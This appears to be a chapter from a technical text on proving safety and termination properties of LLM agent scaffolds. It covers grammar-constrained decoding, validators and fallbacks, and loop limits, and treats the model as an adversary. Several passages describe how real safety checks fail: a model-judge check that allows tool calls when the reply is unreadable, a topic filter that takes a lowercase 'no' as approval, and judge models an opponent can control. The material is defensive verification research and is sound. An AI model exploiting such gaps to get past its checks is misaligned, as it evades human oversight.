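Parsers usually work in two stages. A lexer groups characters into symbols, such as numbers or the keyword `true`, and the parser checks the order of the symbols. A model's tokens don't always match these symbols. One token may contain all of `true`, only `tru`, or two symbols, such as `}]`. After the token `1`, the lexer can't determine whether the number is complete, because the next token might be another digit.

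A simple checker tests every token in the vocabulary by appending it to the output so far and running the lexer and parser on the result. In *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, Park, Zhou and D'Antoni (2025) found that Outlines, which works this way, took 3 to 15 seconds per token on grammars for Go, Java and Python. Faster tools do most of the work in advance, which can introduce errors. In the same tests, SynCode masked valid tokens with the Go grammar. XGrammar could not compile the Java grammar, and it looped forever or crashed on the Go and Python grammars.

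For a safety proof, SynCode's error is harmless. The crashes and loops count as failed calls, which the scaffold has to handle anyway.

Park and colleagues built their own tool, GreatGramma. Before generation starts, it works out which symbols each token can complete from each state of the lexer, plus one symbol that could come next. In the example, reading `+` after `1` completes a number and starts a plus sign, which gives the sequence "number, plus". GreatGramma then sorts these sequences:

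- "Number, plus" is acceptable at this point however many parentheses are open, so the tool always allows the tokens that produce it.
- "Number, number" is never acceptable there.
- "Number, closing parenthesis" depends on whether a parenthesis is open, so the tool checks this during generation.

GreatGramma's preparation took 25 seconds to about four minutes for each grammar and vocabulary, and it then needed 5 to 32 milliseconds per token. SynCode's preparation took 9 to 54 minutes.

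### The Lean proof of GreatGramma

Bhat and colleagues wrote GreatGramma's checker in Lean and proved it correct, in what they believe is the first machine-checked proof of a whole constrained-decoding algorithm. For every viable prefix $w$ and token $v$, the theorem states that

$$\text{the checker allows } v \text{ after } w \iff \exists u \in V^*:\ \text{detok}(wvu) \in L,$$

and that the checker allows the end marker exactly when $\text{detok}(w) \in L$. The mask is therefore both sound and complete, under these assumptions:

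- **Vocabulary:** No token is empty, and every single character is also a token. Otherwise there might be a grammatical continuation that no sequence of tokens can spell.
- **Lexer:** It never produces an empty symbol, and it has no dead ends, so every partial symbol it accepts can still become a complete one.
- **Parser:** It has no dead ends either.
- **Whitespace:** Some whitespace character ends any symbol before it, cannot be part of any other symbol, and makes no difference to the parser.

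GreatGramma needs the whitespace assumption because it looks only one symbol past those that a token completes, and relies on the lexer being able to produce any further symbols the parser might require. Without a separator, adjacent symbols can merge. For example, if a grammar allows a list of numbers, the lexer reads `1` followed by `2` as 12. A separator keeps the symbols apart, so the lexer can produce any sequence the parser requires.

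Bhat and colleagues proved that all the assumptions hold for a simple version of JSON, using the newline as the separator. A space would not work, because it can be part of a JSON string. In Python and YAML, line breaks and indentation carry meaning, so inserting whitespace can change a program or make it invalid. The theorem may not apply to these languages. Park and colleagues measured their tool on three languages, including Python.

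The proof also uncovered a bug in the published algorithm. To let the model stop before writing anything, Park and colleagues allowed the end marker whenever the lexer was in its start state. But some lexers can return to that state in the middle of a symbol. For example, the regular expression `(ab)*a` matches `a`, `aba`, `ababa` and so on. After `ab`, the lexer is back in its start state, so the checker lets the model stop, although `ab` is not a complete symbol. This makes the checker unsound, which could invalidate a proof about a scaffold. Bhat and colleagues fixed the bug by adding a separate start state that the lexer never re-enters while reading a symbol.

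The theorem covers the Lean checker, not the fast Python tool. To make verification easier, Bhat and colleagues gave the Lean checker an exponential-time algorithm for finding the symbols that can come next. In the theorem, $L$ is whatever the given lexer and parser accept. In Java, the `>>` at the end of `List<List<T>>` closes two brackets, but a lexer that always takes the longest match reads it as a single shift operator. A checker built on that lexer would mask valid Java without contradicting the theorem.

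### The refund agent with a grammar

Suppose the refund agent's model may produce only these replies:

```
reply   ::=  {"refund": amount}  |  {"reply": string}
amount  ::=  0  |  a digit from 1 to 9, then any further digits
```

In the safer abstract program from earlier, the opponent chooses a raw string `s`, which the parser then turns into `r`. A sound mask lets the prover add an assumption about every reply that finishes normally:

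```
havoc s
assume s in L
r := parse(s)
```

By the rules for `havoc` and `assume`, the proof now has to establish

$$\forall s \in L.\ wp(r := \text{parse}(s),\ Q)$$

and no longer has to consider strings outside $L$. If the prover also shows that `parse` turns every string in $L$ into a `Refund` or a `Reply`, parse errors disappear from the proof. So do negative amounts. The grammar also rules out replies that give the amount twice, which two parsers could read differently.

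The refund amount can still be any whole number. For example, `{"refund": 5000}` is in $L$. Without the guard, the weakest precondition for the cap would require $paid + x \leq 100$ for every whole number $x \geq 0$, which is false in every state. The opponent can also still leave the customer without an answer by requesting 5,000 three times.

A grammar that allows only amounts from 0 to 100 has the same effect as the faulty guard `x <= 100`, which ignores earlier payments, so the scaffold still needs a correct guard. Alternatively, the scaffold can send a new grammar with each call that allows only amounts up to `100 - paid`. The agent would then stay within the cap without a guard, but the payment limit would depend on the decoder, when one line in the scaffold could enforce the same limit.

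On the third call, the scaffold can also switch to a grammar that allows only a `Reply`. If that call finishes normally, the customer is certain to get a message, but the message could be empty or nonsense, and no grammar can establish that the customer deserves a refund.

### Running out of tokens

A viable prefix can be completed grammatically, but the completion may not fit within the token limit. After `{"reply": "`, the model can keep adding words to the message indefinitely, and every prefix is viable. If the model reaches the limit before writing the closing quotation mark, the scaffold receives a string outside $L$.

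Collura, Tit and colleagues (2026), in *Stay Within Your Bounds*, present a decoder called SWYB that keeps track of how many tokens it would take to finish. Their example language consists of balanced parentheses followed by a single `x`, and the limit is three tokens. An ordinary mask would allow `(((`, which is viable at every step but incomplete at the limit. SWYB compares the distance to a complete string with the tokens left:

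| Text so far | Next token | Shortest ending afterwards | Tokens left afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| empty | `(` | `)x` (2 tokens) | 2 | keep |
| `(` | `(` | `))x` (3 tokens) | 1 | discard |
| `(` | `)` | `x` (1 token) | 1 | keep |
| `()` | `x` | nothing | 0 | keep |

SWYB computes these distances in advance. It represents the grammar as a pushdown automaton, a state machine with a stack that records, for instance, which brackets are open. It measures the length of each symbol as the smallest number of tokens that can spell it, then finds the shortest route from each state and stack to a complete string, up to a fixed stack height. During generation, it considers tokens from the automaton alongside the model's most likely tokens, so that a route to completion is available even if the model gives it a low probability.

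Their theorem guarantees that every output SWYB returns is grammatical, and that SWYB returns an output if the distance from the start is within the token limit. If the distance is larger, SWYB reports that it cannot certify completion. A short enough output may still exist, since the calculation ignores stacks above the fixed height.

The first part holds because SWYB returns only outputs that the automaton accepts. The second part needs a correction because the paper defines the distance by the automaton's state and stack, ignoring any half-written symbol. Suppose the only valid output is one keyword that takes two tokens, and the limit is two tokens. After the first token, the automaton has not moved, so the distance is still 2. Only one token is left, so SWYB would discard the only correct path. The distance should count only the remaining tokens of a half-written symbol, and the proof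 appears to rely on this.

With a limit of 120 tokens, SWYB produced valid JSON in all 100 test cases with each of three small models. Five other constrained decoders did so in 88–96% of cases. When the limit was 512 tokens, four of those five reached 95–100%, so a generous limit prevents most truncation but does not rule it out.

SWYB's outputs also always matched the schema, which describes the fields each reply must contain. The other decoders did worse. Collura and colleagues attribute this to a lack of lookahead, but the choice of grammar may explain much of the difference. With one model at 512 tokens, all of SynCode's outputs were valid JSON, but only 83% matched the schema. A decoder that enforced the schema could not have produced this result, so SynCode was probably enforcing only JSON in general, while SWYB had a separate grammar for each schema.

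SWYB took about 0.3 seconds to prepare for each JSON schema, but 3 hours and 40 minutes for the database language SQL with up to three nested queries. Masking can also change answer quality. On SQL tasks with Llama-3.2-3B, 46.3% of queries returned the right result without constraints, compared with 39.6% with SynCode and 51.5% with SWYB.

### What model providers promise

Most scaffolds call a model on a provider's servers, where the developer cannot inspect the decoder. The developer sends a JSON schema with the request and has to rely on the provider's documentation to know what the output is guaranteed to be.

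In Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, the company promises "guaranteed field types and required fields" through constrained decoding. In OpenAI's *Structured outputs*, the promise is that replies will "always" follow the schema. Google likewise describes the feature as guaranteeing adherence to a schema, in *Improving Structured Outputs in the Gemini API* (2025). Anthropic and OpenAI list exceptions further down:

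| | Anthropic | OpenAI |
|---|---|---|
| The model refuses | Reply may not match the schema | Refusal arrives in a separate field |
| The reply reaches the token limit | May be incomplete | May be incomplete |
| The schema lists the permitted words | Capitalization may differ | No exception listed |
| The schema sets a maximum for a number | Not supported | Supported, except for fine-tuned models |

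In its launch announcement, *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API*, OpenAI promised JSON that matches the schema if the reply contains no refusal and nothing interrupted it. The scaffold can check both conditions because the service reports refusals and interruptions along with the reply.

The capitalization exception is harder to notice because, as Anthropic warns, the response completes normally, with no error. Suppose the schema lists "Late delivery" as a permitted reason for a refund. Claude may return "Late Delivery", and a scaffold that looks up the exact words in a table of refund rules would find nothing. If the programmer didn't handle a failed lookup because the schema seemed to rule it out, the agent could crash, and a restart with `paid` at 0 could let it exceed the cap. Anthropic recommends ignoring capitalization when comparing such values.

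Anthropic's JSON setting applies the schema only to the model's direct answer, not to its tool calls or reasoning. If the refund agent requests payments through a tool, the developer has to turn on a separate strict mode for that tool.

With a hosted model, the scaffold should still parse every reply and keep the `Error` case. The schema makes errors rarer, but the proof should not depend on it. A team that runs its own model with a verified checker can prove that finished replies parse. To rule out truncated replies, it also needs a decoder that certifies completion within the token limit.

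## What do output checks and fallbacks add to the proof?

A scaffold that calls a hosted model cannot depend on the provider's decoder, but it can test each reply with a validator before using it. If a reply fails, the scaffold can ask again. If every attempt fails, it can use a fixed, trusted result called the fallback.

For the refund agent, let the validator $V$ accept `Refund(x)` if `paid + x <= 100`, accept every `Reply`, and reject errors. The fallback $d$ is a `Reply` telling the customer that a member of staff will be in touch. With at most $K$ attempts, where $K$ is at least 1, the model call becomes:

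```
tries := 0;  ok := false
while tries < K and not ok:
    tries := tries + 1
    havoc r              # the model call
    ok := V(r)           # the test
if not ok:
    r := d               # the fallback
```

After this code, `r` passes $V$ whatever the model returned. The validator has already compared `x` with `paid`, so the agent can pay `x` without a further guard.

### The derivation

Start with one attempt, and let $Q(r)$ be the condition wanted afterwards. By the rules for `havoc`, the conditional and assignment, the weakest precondition is

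$$\forall r.\ \big(V(r) \Rightarrow Q(r)\big) \wedge \big(\neg V(r) \Rightarrow Q(d)\big).$$

If $d$ passes $V$, the first part already gives $Q(d)$, so the second part adds nothing. What remains is

$$\forall r.\ \big(V(r) \Rightarrow Q(r)\big),$$

which is the weakest precondition of `havoc r; assume V(r)`. The rest of the proof may therefore assume $V(r)$ for every possible model.

Allowing more attempts doesn't change this. After a rejection, the program runs the same code with one fewer attempt. By induction, that code has the same weakest precondition, which the accepted case already requires. So the proof establishes no more with 100 attempts than with one, but the extra attempts make the agent more likely to use a reply from the model instead of the fallback.

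The derivation requires that the validator return an answer for every reply and have no side effects. The fallback must also pass in every state the agent can reach. A goodwill payment of `Refund(20)` would be a bad fallback because it fails the test when `paid` is 90. Since $V$ depends on `paid`, its result is valid only until `paid` changes, so nothing else may pay the customer between the test and the payment.

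### Assuming without testing

If the verified program contains `havoc r; assume V(r)` but the running agent has neither the test nor the guard, the proof of the cap still succeeds but doesn't protect the shop. A bare model call refines `havoc r; assume V(r)` only if the model never returns a reply that fails $V$, and nobody has proved that. The code with the test and the fallback does refine it, because every path ends with an `r` that passes $V$.

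A scaffold that tests replies but has no fallback must still do something after the last rejection. Using the rejected reply invalidates the proof, and asking again without limit may never end. The scaffold can also stop. *Soteria* (2026), a system that runs agents according to verified plans, combines retrying and stopping. It blocks any tool call the plan does not allow and reports the error to the model, which can try something else. But if a tool runs and its result violates the tool's stated postcondition, Soteria aborts the run, because the contract the plan relied on was wrong. Stopping keeps later payments from breaking the cap but leaves the customer without an answer.

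### Guarded calls in SEVerA

SEVerA, a system by Banerjee and colleagues, puts a test and a fallback around every model call. A planner model writes the agent in a subset of Dafny and may call other models only through a wrapper. For each wrapper, the planner supplies a precondition $\Phi$, a postcondition $\Psi$, code that builds the prompt, code that extracts the answer from the raw output, and a fallback. Dafny must prove that the fallback satisfies $\Psi$ whenever $\Phi$ holds.

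At run time the wrapper draws up to five outputs and returns the first that satisfies $\Psi$. After each rejection, it adds the failed parts of $\Psi$ to the next prompt. Banerjee and colleagues call this a stateful rejection sampler. In ordinary rejection sampling the draws are independent, so the accepted outputs keep their relative probabilities under the model. Changing the prompt loses this property, but the proof requires only that the wrapper never returns a rejected output.

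The wrapper can test $\Psi$ exactly because $\Psi$ contains no "for all" or "there is" and uses only functions that always return a result. Whatever the wrapper returns has therefore either passed the test or come from the verified fallback. If $\theta$ stands for the model's parameters and $g_\theta$ for the wrapped call, this gives

$$\text{for all } \theta \text{ and all } x:\quad \Phi(x) \Rightarrow \Psi(x, g_\theta(x)).$$

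Dafny then verifies the agent from these postconditions alone, as it did with `CallModel`, but the postcondition now provides a useful guarantee. By the soundness theorem, every agent that SEVerA returns meets the user's specification on all valid inputs and for all parameter values. Fine-tuning only replaces one $\theta$ with another, so it cannot invalidate the proof.

In one of the paper's examples, the task is to recover the formula $\sqrt{1.23x}$ from noisy data. The specification requires the result to be at least $x^{0.8}$ for $x$ between 0 and 1, and at least $\sqrt{x}$ for larger $x$. One candidate program returned $ax + b$, with small neural networks choosing $a$ and $b$ between 0 and 1. It failed verification because $a$ and $b$ could both be 0. Another returned $ax^d$ with $a$ between 1 and 1.5 and $d$ between 0.5 and 0.8, which meets both bounds for every choice in those ranges.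 If a network produces a number outside its range, the fallback changes it to the nearest end of that range. Training then produced $a = 1.11$ and $d = 0.503$, very close to the true formula.

The theorem depends on the contracts of the library functions, the axioms about them, and Dafny's translation of the agent into Python, none of which SEVerA checks. In the customer-service agents, the fallback hands the customer to a human, and an axiom states that this always complies with policy. If an airline required an identity check before any transfer, the axiom would be false and the verified fallback would break the rule.

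### What the fallback costs

Banerjee and colleagues tested SEVerA on three kinds of task with language models. On HumanEvalDafny and DafnyBench, the agent adds proof annotations to a program without changing the program itself. On τ²-bench, it handles customer-service requests. On GSM-Symbolic, it writes a formula that answers a school maths problem. The table gives success rates, and the last column shows how often the fallback supplied the final output:

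| Benchmark | SEVerA | Best baseline | Same search without constraints | Fallback used |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| HumanEvalDafny | 97.0% | 86.9% | 84.8% | 5.1% |
| DafnyBench | 89.1% | 81.6% | 79.2% | 7.9% |
| τ²-bench retail | 53.6% | 42.2% | 49.4% | 15.6% |
| τ²-bench airline | 52.6% | 39.4% | 44.7% | 21.6% |
| GSM-Symbolic | 66.0% | 44.7% | not reported | 2.1% |

SEVerA had no violations, as the theorem guarantees. Without constraints, the same search produced agents that broke the rules in 5.1% to 25.5% of cases. The main experimental result is therefore the success rates, some of which come from small samples. SEVerA solved 20 of the 38 airline tasks, and the baseline solved 15. On GSM-Symbolic, SEVerA solved 31 of 47 problems, and the baseline solved 21. More than half of that gap came from fine-tuning, since SEVerA solved 25 problems (53.2%) without it.

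The fallbacks are safe but seldom solve the task. Depending on the task, they return the original program unchanged, return the formula "0", or transfer the customer to a human. For example, an agent that transferred every airline customer to a human would satisfy its contract but solve only about one task in twenty. Used alone, the fallbacks succeeded in at most 5.4% of cases, except on DafnyBench, where 29.3% of the programs needed no annotations.

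On HumanEvalDafny, retrying with feedback on which conditions had failed cut the use of the fallback from 9.1% to 5.1%, and success rose from 88.8% to 97.0%.

Banerjee and colleagues also prove that guarding a model need not lower its total score, provided that the scoring rule ranks every permitted output above every forbidden one. This is a strong condition, because a shop might well prefer a deserved refund of 101, which breaks the cap, to a polite message that solves nothing.

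### Checks in existing agents

Most agents have no verified contract around their model calls. In *When Code Becomes an LLM Call*, Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026) examined 496 places where a program calls a model, across 40 popular open-source agent systems, to find out which checks were missing. This is hard to do by reading code, because a missing check leaves no trace and an analyst who has seen the code tends to accept its omissions.

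They therefore split the work among four AI agents with separate contexts. The first read the code and described what the call had to achieve, but not how the program did it. The second saw only this description and derived the constraints the call needed. For each constraint, it had to give a concrete failure that would happen without it, and the constraint could not rule out legitimate replies or repeat another. The third saw only the code and listed the constraints the code enforced, and the fourth compared the two lists. Human reviewers checked every step, in full or on a sample.

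Of the 917 model outputs, 48% decide what the program does next or run as code. Code checks run both before and after the call at 82% of call sites. Even so, the programs failed to meet 63% of the 2,699 expected constraints, and only 26 of 492 sites (5.3%) met their whole contract. Usually the code checked the right property but missed some values or paths. Another 268 constraints appeared only in prompts, although code could have checked them. For example, the trading system TradingAgents prompts the model for at most eight indicators with exact names, but its code checks only that the reply contains a tool call.

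The 63% depends on judgments about what each call needs, and the agent that wrote the descriptions had seen the code. Reviewers found 48 descriptions that revealed implementation details, but excluding them changed the result by less than one percentage point.

Two of the faults match steps in the derivation. STORM, a system that writes articles, asks a model whether a topic is acceptable and requests "Yes." or "No." as the answer. The code rejects the topic only if the reply begins with "No", so a lowercase "no" or a refusal to answer counts as approval. When a topic passes this test, a proof could assume only that the reply does not begin with "No".

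The other fault is a bad fallback. Gemini CLI, a coding agent, has an optional safety check in which a model judges whether a tool call complies with a policy. If the reply is empty or unreadable, or the request fails, the code allows the call. The model has not judged that call compliant, so a proof about the code that runs next cannot assume that every allowed call complies. Falling back to "deny" would fix this.

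Weng and colleagues ruled out 83% of the 1,697 gaps as security problems, often because they arose before there was a reply or because another check stopped the bad value. They traced 114 gaps to 60 ways of causing harm and triggered 38 of them, 36 with a real model. Some needed no attacker. For example, in JARVIS, which passes tasks to other models, the model invented tool names that happened to exist in the full catalogue but were not among those offered.

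For each of the 38, they wrote a small patch that enforced the missing constraint. The patches stopped the original attack in all 38 cases and a variation of it in 35, but fully fixed the problem in only 23. Some of the rest needed a judgment about meaning that simple code could not make, and others needed a stronger sandbox. Of the 22 that never triggered, 15 failed because the model or the provider's safety system refused, and a different model might not.

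### Which conditions can a validator decide?

Amer and colleagues treat a policy as a set of forbidden strings and call a check exact if it blocks every forbidden string and passes every permitted one. If a model can output any finite string, an exact check exists if and only if the policy is decidable, meaning that some algorithm can correctly determine whether any given string is forbidden. Every check for an undecidable policy makes infinitely many mistakes, because if there were only finitely many, we could make the check exact by adding a list of corrections.

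A check can always determine whether an output contains a phrase from a banned list, but by a version of Rice's theorem, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it will ever perform a harmful action.

Real replies have a length limit, so only finitely many are possible, and a table listing every forbidden reply would in principle be an exact check. But Amer and colleagues prove that, for an undecidable policy, no single algorithm can produce the correct table for every length limit. If one could, we could decide whether any string was forbidden by building the table for its length and looking the string up.

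The program that performs a forbidden action only if Goldbach's conjecture is false easily fits in 500 tokens, so a correct table has an entry for it, but nobody knows what that entry should be. The table would also need to cover about $10^{2500}$ replies. A shorter method may exist for a particular policy, but this isn't guaranteed. Amer and colleagues cite a result that, under cryptographic assumptions, an exact filter can exist even when no efficient one does.

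However, a safety proof only needs the check to reject every forbidden reply, as with grammar masks, so the check does not have to be exact. SEVerA, for example, rejects any program its planner writes that Dafny cannot prove correct within the time limit, even though the program may be correct. Undecidability therefore makes the scaffold less useful, because the check rejects some good replies, but it does not invalidate the proof.

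The scaffold can often avoid the difficulty by checking actions instead of text, as the guarded `refund(x)` operation does for generated programs. Amer and colleagues prove that a monitor can enforce a ban on specified actions exactly if it sees every action and can stop it. Checking actions does not help when the text itself is harmful. If a policy forbids sending false mathematical statements to a customer, the monitor still has to decide whether each statement is true before the agent sends it.

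When the scaffold lacks the facts to check a condition, such as whether the customer deserves the refund, it can require a person's approval. The proof may then assume only that the approval exists. For example, *Agenra* (2026), an authorization system with a core verified in Lean, checks that an approval exists and uses it up, but relies on the reviewer to have judged correctly.

Asking a second model to judge the reply has the same limit. The second model's verdict is also an arbitrary value, so after a "yes" the proof may assume only that the model returned "yes". An opponent who controls both models can make the second approve whatever the first proposes. Such a judge may catch many bad refunds in practice, but proving the cap still requires the comparison with `paid`.

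## Can it be proved that the task gets finished?

With a validator and a fallback, the refund agent always ends up with an acceptable reply. But that reply may be the fallback message promising that staff will be in touch, which does not settle the complaint. "The agent finishes" can therefore mean several things:

- **Halting:** every run ends.
- **Correct reporting:** when a run ends, the agent's report of success or failure is true.
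- **Completion:** every run ends with the task done.

No model can keep a scaffold running forever if the scaffold limits the number of model calls, or make its report false if the scaffold bases the report on its own records and checks. The refund agent, for example, sets `answered` to true only after `send` has returned, so when it reports that "a message went out", that is true whatever the model does.

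We can prove that a scaffold completes a task whatever the model replies only if the task never needed the model. Such a scaffold would have to complete the task even when every reply is an empty string. A program can produce empty strings by itself, so the task would still get done if the model were removed. For any other task, the model can prevent completion by returning useless replies for as long as the scaffold keeps querying it.

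### Halting

The refund agent halts, provided that each pass ends, because the variant `3 - calls` starts at 3 and falls by 1 on every pass. A quantity that only usually falls would not prove that the agent halts. *Semantic Early-Stopping for Iterative LLM Agent Loops* (Shrivastava, 2026) studied a loop in which one model drafts an answer and another criticises it. The loop can stop early when successive drafts barely differ in meaning. An earlier version of the project claimed a theorem that the drafts converge to a fixed point, but Shrivastava withdrew it because nothing supported its main assumption. On 60 test questions, the distance between successive drafts fell on average, but it fell at every round in only about 5% of runs.

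The remaining theorem states that the loop halts within a fixed number of rounds for any drafts, even adversarial ones. Its proof uses only the round counter and a final test that no setting can switch off. The theorem does not cover quality. In the experiment, stopping after the first draft used 86% fewer tokens than running all six rounds, with no detectable loss of quality.

The number of remaining faults can also serve as a variant if the scaffold makes it fall. In *Post-SQLFix* (Guo, Wu and colleagues, 2026), a model repairs database queries, and a monitor accepts a repair only if it reduces the number of rule violations. A query with five violations can therefore have at most five accepted repairs. Rejected repairs leave the count unchanged, so the loop also needs a limit on retries.

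A query can have zero violations and still be wrong. In one example, the user wanted the district for order 33333. The model's repair removed the last violation but also dropped the condition that selected this order, so the query would have returned the district for every account. The monitor rejected the repair only because it also checks that repairs keep existing conditions.

### Agents with no effective limit

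In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) searched 6,549 open-source agent projects for loops that might never end. Their tool builds a graph of each program, including the links that agent frameworks create implicitly. It looks for cycles that repeat model calls or other costly steps and checks whether a limit covers the whole cycle. It does not count an exit that depends on the model's output as a limit, which is the right rule when the model could output anything.

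The tool reported 74 loops, and manual review confirmed 68 of them, in 47 projects:

| What repeats without an effective limit | Confirmed cases |
|---|---|
| Retries after a failure | 17 |
| Tool calls | 16 |
| Conversation between agents | 14 |
| A cycle in a workflow | 9 |
| Messages fed back into the agent | 7 |
| Delegation, evaluation or restarting of an agent | 5 |

In an assistant published by NVIDIA, for example, if the model returns neither a tool call nor any text, the code adds the message "Respond with a real output." and asks again, in a loop with no limit. If the model kept returning nothing, the loop would keep running, and each call would cost more because the conversation gets longer. Another project, LiteRAG, asks for a plan until one parses and passes a check, and ignores the parser's errors.

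The 47 projects are 0.7% of the sample, but this is a lower bound because the tool handles only eight frameworks, looks only for loops visible in the source code, and may filter out real cases.

A program can also have a limit in the wrong place. In an example from Hou and colleagues, a cap on an inner agent's turns does not limit an outer loop that keeps restarting that agent.

### When a later step sends work back

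Restarts are useful when a later step reveals a problem in an earlier one. *Bounded Loops* (Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj, 2026) proves that agents with such restarts halt. Each step in the system has a worker (usually an agent), a gate that checks the result, and a budget of attempts. The worker cannot change the gate, and the gate does not read the worker's account of what it did. The steps form a graph without cycles, and each step waits for the ones it depends on.

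Suppose the shop has one step that gathers evidence about a complaint and another that writes the decision, with three attempts each. The evidence may pass its gate and still lack a receipt that the decision needs. The decision step then fails all three attempts, however well its worker writes. A repair edge sends the work back to the evidence step after such a failure.

The repair has to restore the budgets that both steps have used up. The decision step has no attempts left, so it couldn't use new evidence without a new budget. But restoring the budgets increases the total number of attempts left, so that total can't serve as the variant, though it is the obvious choice.

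Bhardwaj and colleagues solve this with a single limit $R$ on repairs in the whole run, which nothing restores. Their measure is the pair (repairs left, attempts left), compared like words in a dictionary, as in Filliâtre's proof with two counters. An attempt lowers the second number and leaves the first alone. A repair lowers the first, so the pair falls even though the second number rises. With $R = 1$, the longest run looks like this:

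| Event | Repairs left | Attempts left |
|---|---|---|
| Start | 1 | 6 |
| Evidence passes on the third attempt | 1 | 3 |
| Decision fails three times | 1 | 0 |
| Repair sends the work back | 0 | 6 |
| Evidence passes on the third attempt | 0 | 3 |
| Decision fails three times | 0 | 0 |

The run halts after 12 attempts. In general, if step $v$ may make $m_v$ attempts per pass, then

$$\text{total attempts} \leq (R+1)\sum_v m_v,$$

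because there is one original pass and at most $R$ repeats, and each spends at most the full budget. An operator can work this out before starting the run. The proof assumes that every attempt returns and that no step is waiting for a person's approval.

The repair budget must be global, although the other budgets belong to individual steps. Bhardwaj and colleagues warn that a run may never end if each step has its own repair budget. A single repair edge is enough to cause this. When the decision step sends work back to the evidence step, every step that depends on the evidence step restarts, including the decision step. If the restart restores the decision step's own repair budget, it can send the work back again and again. The paper's own example uses two steps that repair each other, which its definition rules out because a step may send work back only to a step it depends on.

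The repair budget must therefore never be restored. Separate budgets would also work if none were ever restored, and the total number of repairs would be at most their sum. A single counter is simpler, but it must survive a crash. Bhardwaj and colleagues' scaffold counts repairs from a saved log, because a counter in memory would return to zero at each restart. When they removed this safeguard, the test for it never finished.

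Proving that a task gets finished is harder, even in principle, than proving that the process halts. Bhardwaj and colleagues cite results on Petri nets, an older formalism for workflows. When steps can restore spent budgets, an algorithm can still decide whether a process halts, but no algorithm can decide for every process whether it can always complete properly.

### What a report of success is worth

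In *Bounded Loops*, a run may end with the status "done" only if the log shows that every step passed its gate. The proof covers any worker, because no test in the program uses the worker's own claim to have finished. Other systems rely on that claim, so an arbitrary model could declare success in its first reply. Bhardwaj and colleagues describe one such system, a harness that DeepSeek released in August 2026, whose documentation calls completion "worker self-declaration".

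But passing a gate guarantees a correct report only if the gate itself is right. Bhardwaj and colleagues tested the gates in their own catalogue of 69 ready-made loops by damaging correct results and checking whether the gates still passed them. They found 47 gate defects in code that had already passed review. One gate checked that an account book's debits equalled its credits and that every transaction had a category. An empty book satisfies both conditions, so a worker could pass by deleting all the transactions. Another gate was meant to catch invented legal citations, but it detected only citations to the law reports on its list, so it missed invented citations to any others.

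After repairs, the gates accepted none of 209 damaged results, but this was weak evidence because the same kinds of damage had guided the repairs. Bhardwaj and colleagues then left the gates unchanged and tried new kinds of damage, which kept a document's structure but removed its content. The gates accepted 14 of 60 such results (23.3%), including a data-protection agreement with all the required headings and nothing under them.

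The share of the system's success reports that are false may differ from 23.3%, because it also depends on how often workers produce bad results. The rate is irrelevant for a worker that can return anything, since that worker could submit a bad result that passes on its first attempt. A proof may therefore assume only that the gate accepted the result. Proving that the task is finished also requires showing that the gate never accepts unfinished work. A sound proof checker meets this requirement for a program with a complete specification.

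More attempts also give a faulty gate more chances to accept bad work. If a gate independently accepts each bad result with probability 5%, the probability of a false report of success within ten bad results is $1 - 0.95^{10}$, or about 40%.

Reports of failure can mislead as well. One of Bhardwaj and colleagues' loops used up all its attempts and halted, as the theorem predicts. The agent program had exited each time without doing anything, because the harness had not passed it a setting it needed. From the log, it looked as if the worker had tried and failed.

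### Fairness

To prove that the task gets finished, we have to assume that the model eventually sends a usable output. For the refund agent, an output is usable if it is a `Reply` that passes the validator. Assuming only that the model eventually sends a valid output would be too weak, because the opponent could request a refund of 0 on every call. Each request would be valid, but the customer would never get an answer.

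A fairness assumption rules out infinite runs in which some event keeps being possible but stops happening. It has two standard forms. As before, GF means "infinitely often", and FG means "from some point on, always":

$$\text{weak fairness:}\quad \text{FG possible} \rightarrow \text{GF happens}$$

$$\text{strong fairness:}\quad \text{GF possible} \rightarrow \text{GF happens}$$

*Progress, Fairness and Justness in Process Algebra* (2015) defines weak fairness, which some authors call justice. Strong fairness implies weak fairness, because an event that is always possible from some point on is also possible infinitely often. *Progress, Justness and Fairness* (2018) warns that in realistic settings weak fairness can be too weak and strong fairness too strong.

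Consider a scaffold that asks until it gets a usable reply:

```
ok := false
while not ok:
    havoc r              # the model call
    ok := usable(r)      # the test
```

A usable reply can arrive only while the scaffold is waiting for the model. In an endless run, the scaffold alternates between waiting and running the test, so a usable reply is possible infinitely often but never continuously. Weak fairness requires a usable reply to arrive only if one remains continuously possible from some point on, so it allows the endless run.

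Strong fairness rules out an endless loop. Suppose the loop never ends. Every call returns and every test finishes, so the scaffold makes infinitely many calls, and a usable reply is possible infinitely often. By strong fairness, usable replies then arrive infinitely often. But the first one sets `ok` to true and ends the loop, which contradicts the assumption. The loop therefore ends with a usable reply.

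This proof gives no limit on the number of calls, because a fair model may return any finite number of errors first. Since no number of passes is certain to be enough, the loop would not count as terminating under Dijkstra's original definition.

### Fairness and a limit of three calls

If the limit of three calls is restored and the model returns three errors, the agent stops without answering the customer. This run is still strongly fair, because strong fairness requires a usable reply only when one is possible infinitely often, and here one was possible only three times. Fairness excludes only infinite runs, so it adds nothing to a proof about a scaffold whose runs are all finite.

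A bounded assumption does make a proof possible. If the model never sends more than $k$ unusable replies in a row, a scaffold that allows at least $k+1$ tries completes its task, because at least one of those replies must be usable. The refund agent allows three calls, so the proof covers it only if $k$ is at most 2. A task that takes $n$ usable replies needs at most $n(k+1)$ calls.

| Assumption about the model | Unlimited tries | At most $K$ tries |
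|---|---|---|
| None | May never halt | Halts, may fail |
| Strong fairness | Completes, with no limit on calls | Halts, may fail |
| At most $k$ unusable replies in a row | Completes within $k+1$ calls | Completes if $K > k$ |

The bounded assumption is a safety property, so the scaffold can detect a violation by counting, whereas no finite log can refute strong fairness. Protocols for distributed agreement face a similar choice between assuming that messages arrive eventually and assuming that they arrive by a fixed deadline. The bounded assumption and strong fairness both have to hold for the prompts the scaffold actually sends, and junk prompts can make them false.

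### How retries fail

Suppose each reply is usable with probability 0.8, independently of the others. The probability that at least one of three is usable is

$$1 - (1 - 0.8)^3 = 0.992.$$

Strong fairness holds with probability 1 if failures are independent, because the probability of $n$ failures in a row is $0.2^n$, which tends to 0. The bounded assumption with $k = 2$ holds for 99.2% of complaints, so a shop with 1,000 complaints should expect about eight to go unanswered.

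*UpSkill* (2026) gives this formula for repeated attempts, but notes that attempts from identical prompts can be strongly correlated. In the extreme case, the model always handles 80% of complaints and never handles the rest. The success rate on the first try is again 80%, but retries don't raise it. For the complaints that always fail, strong fairness and the bounded assumption are both false.

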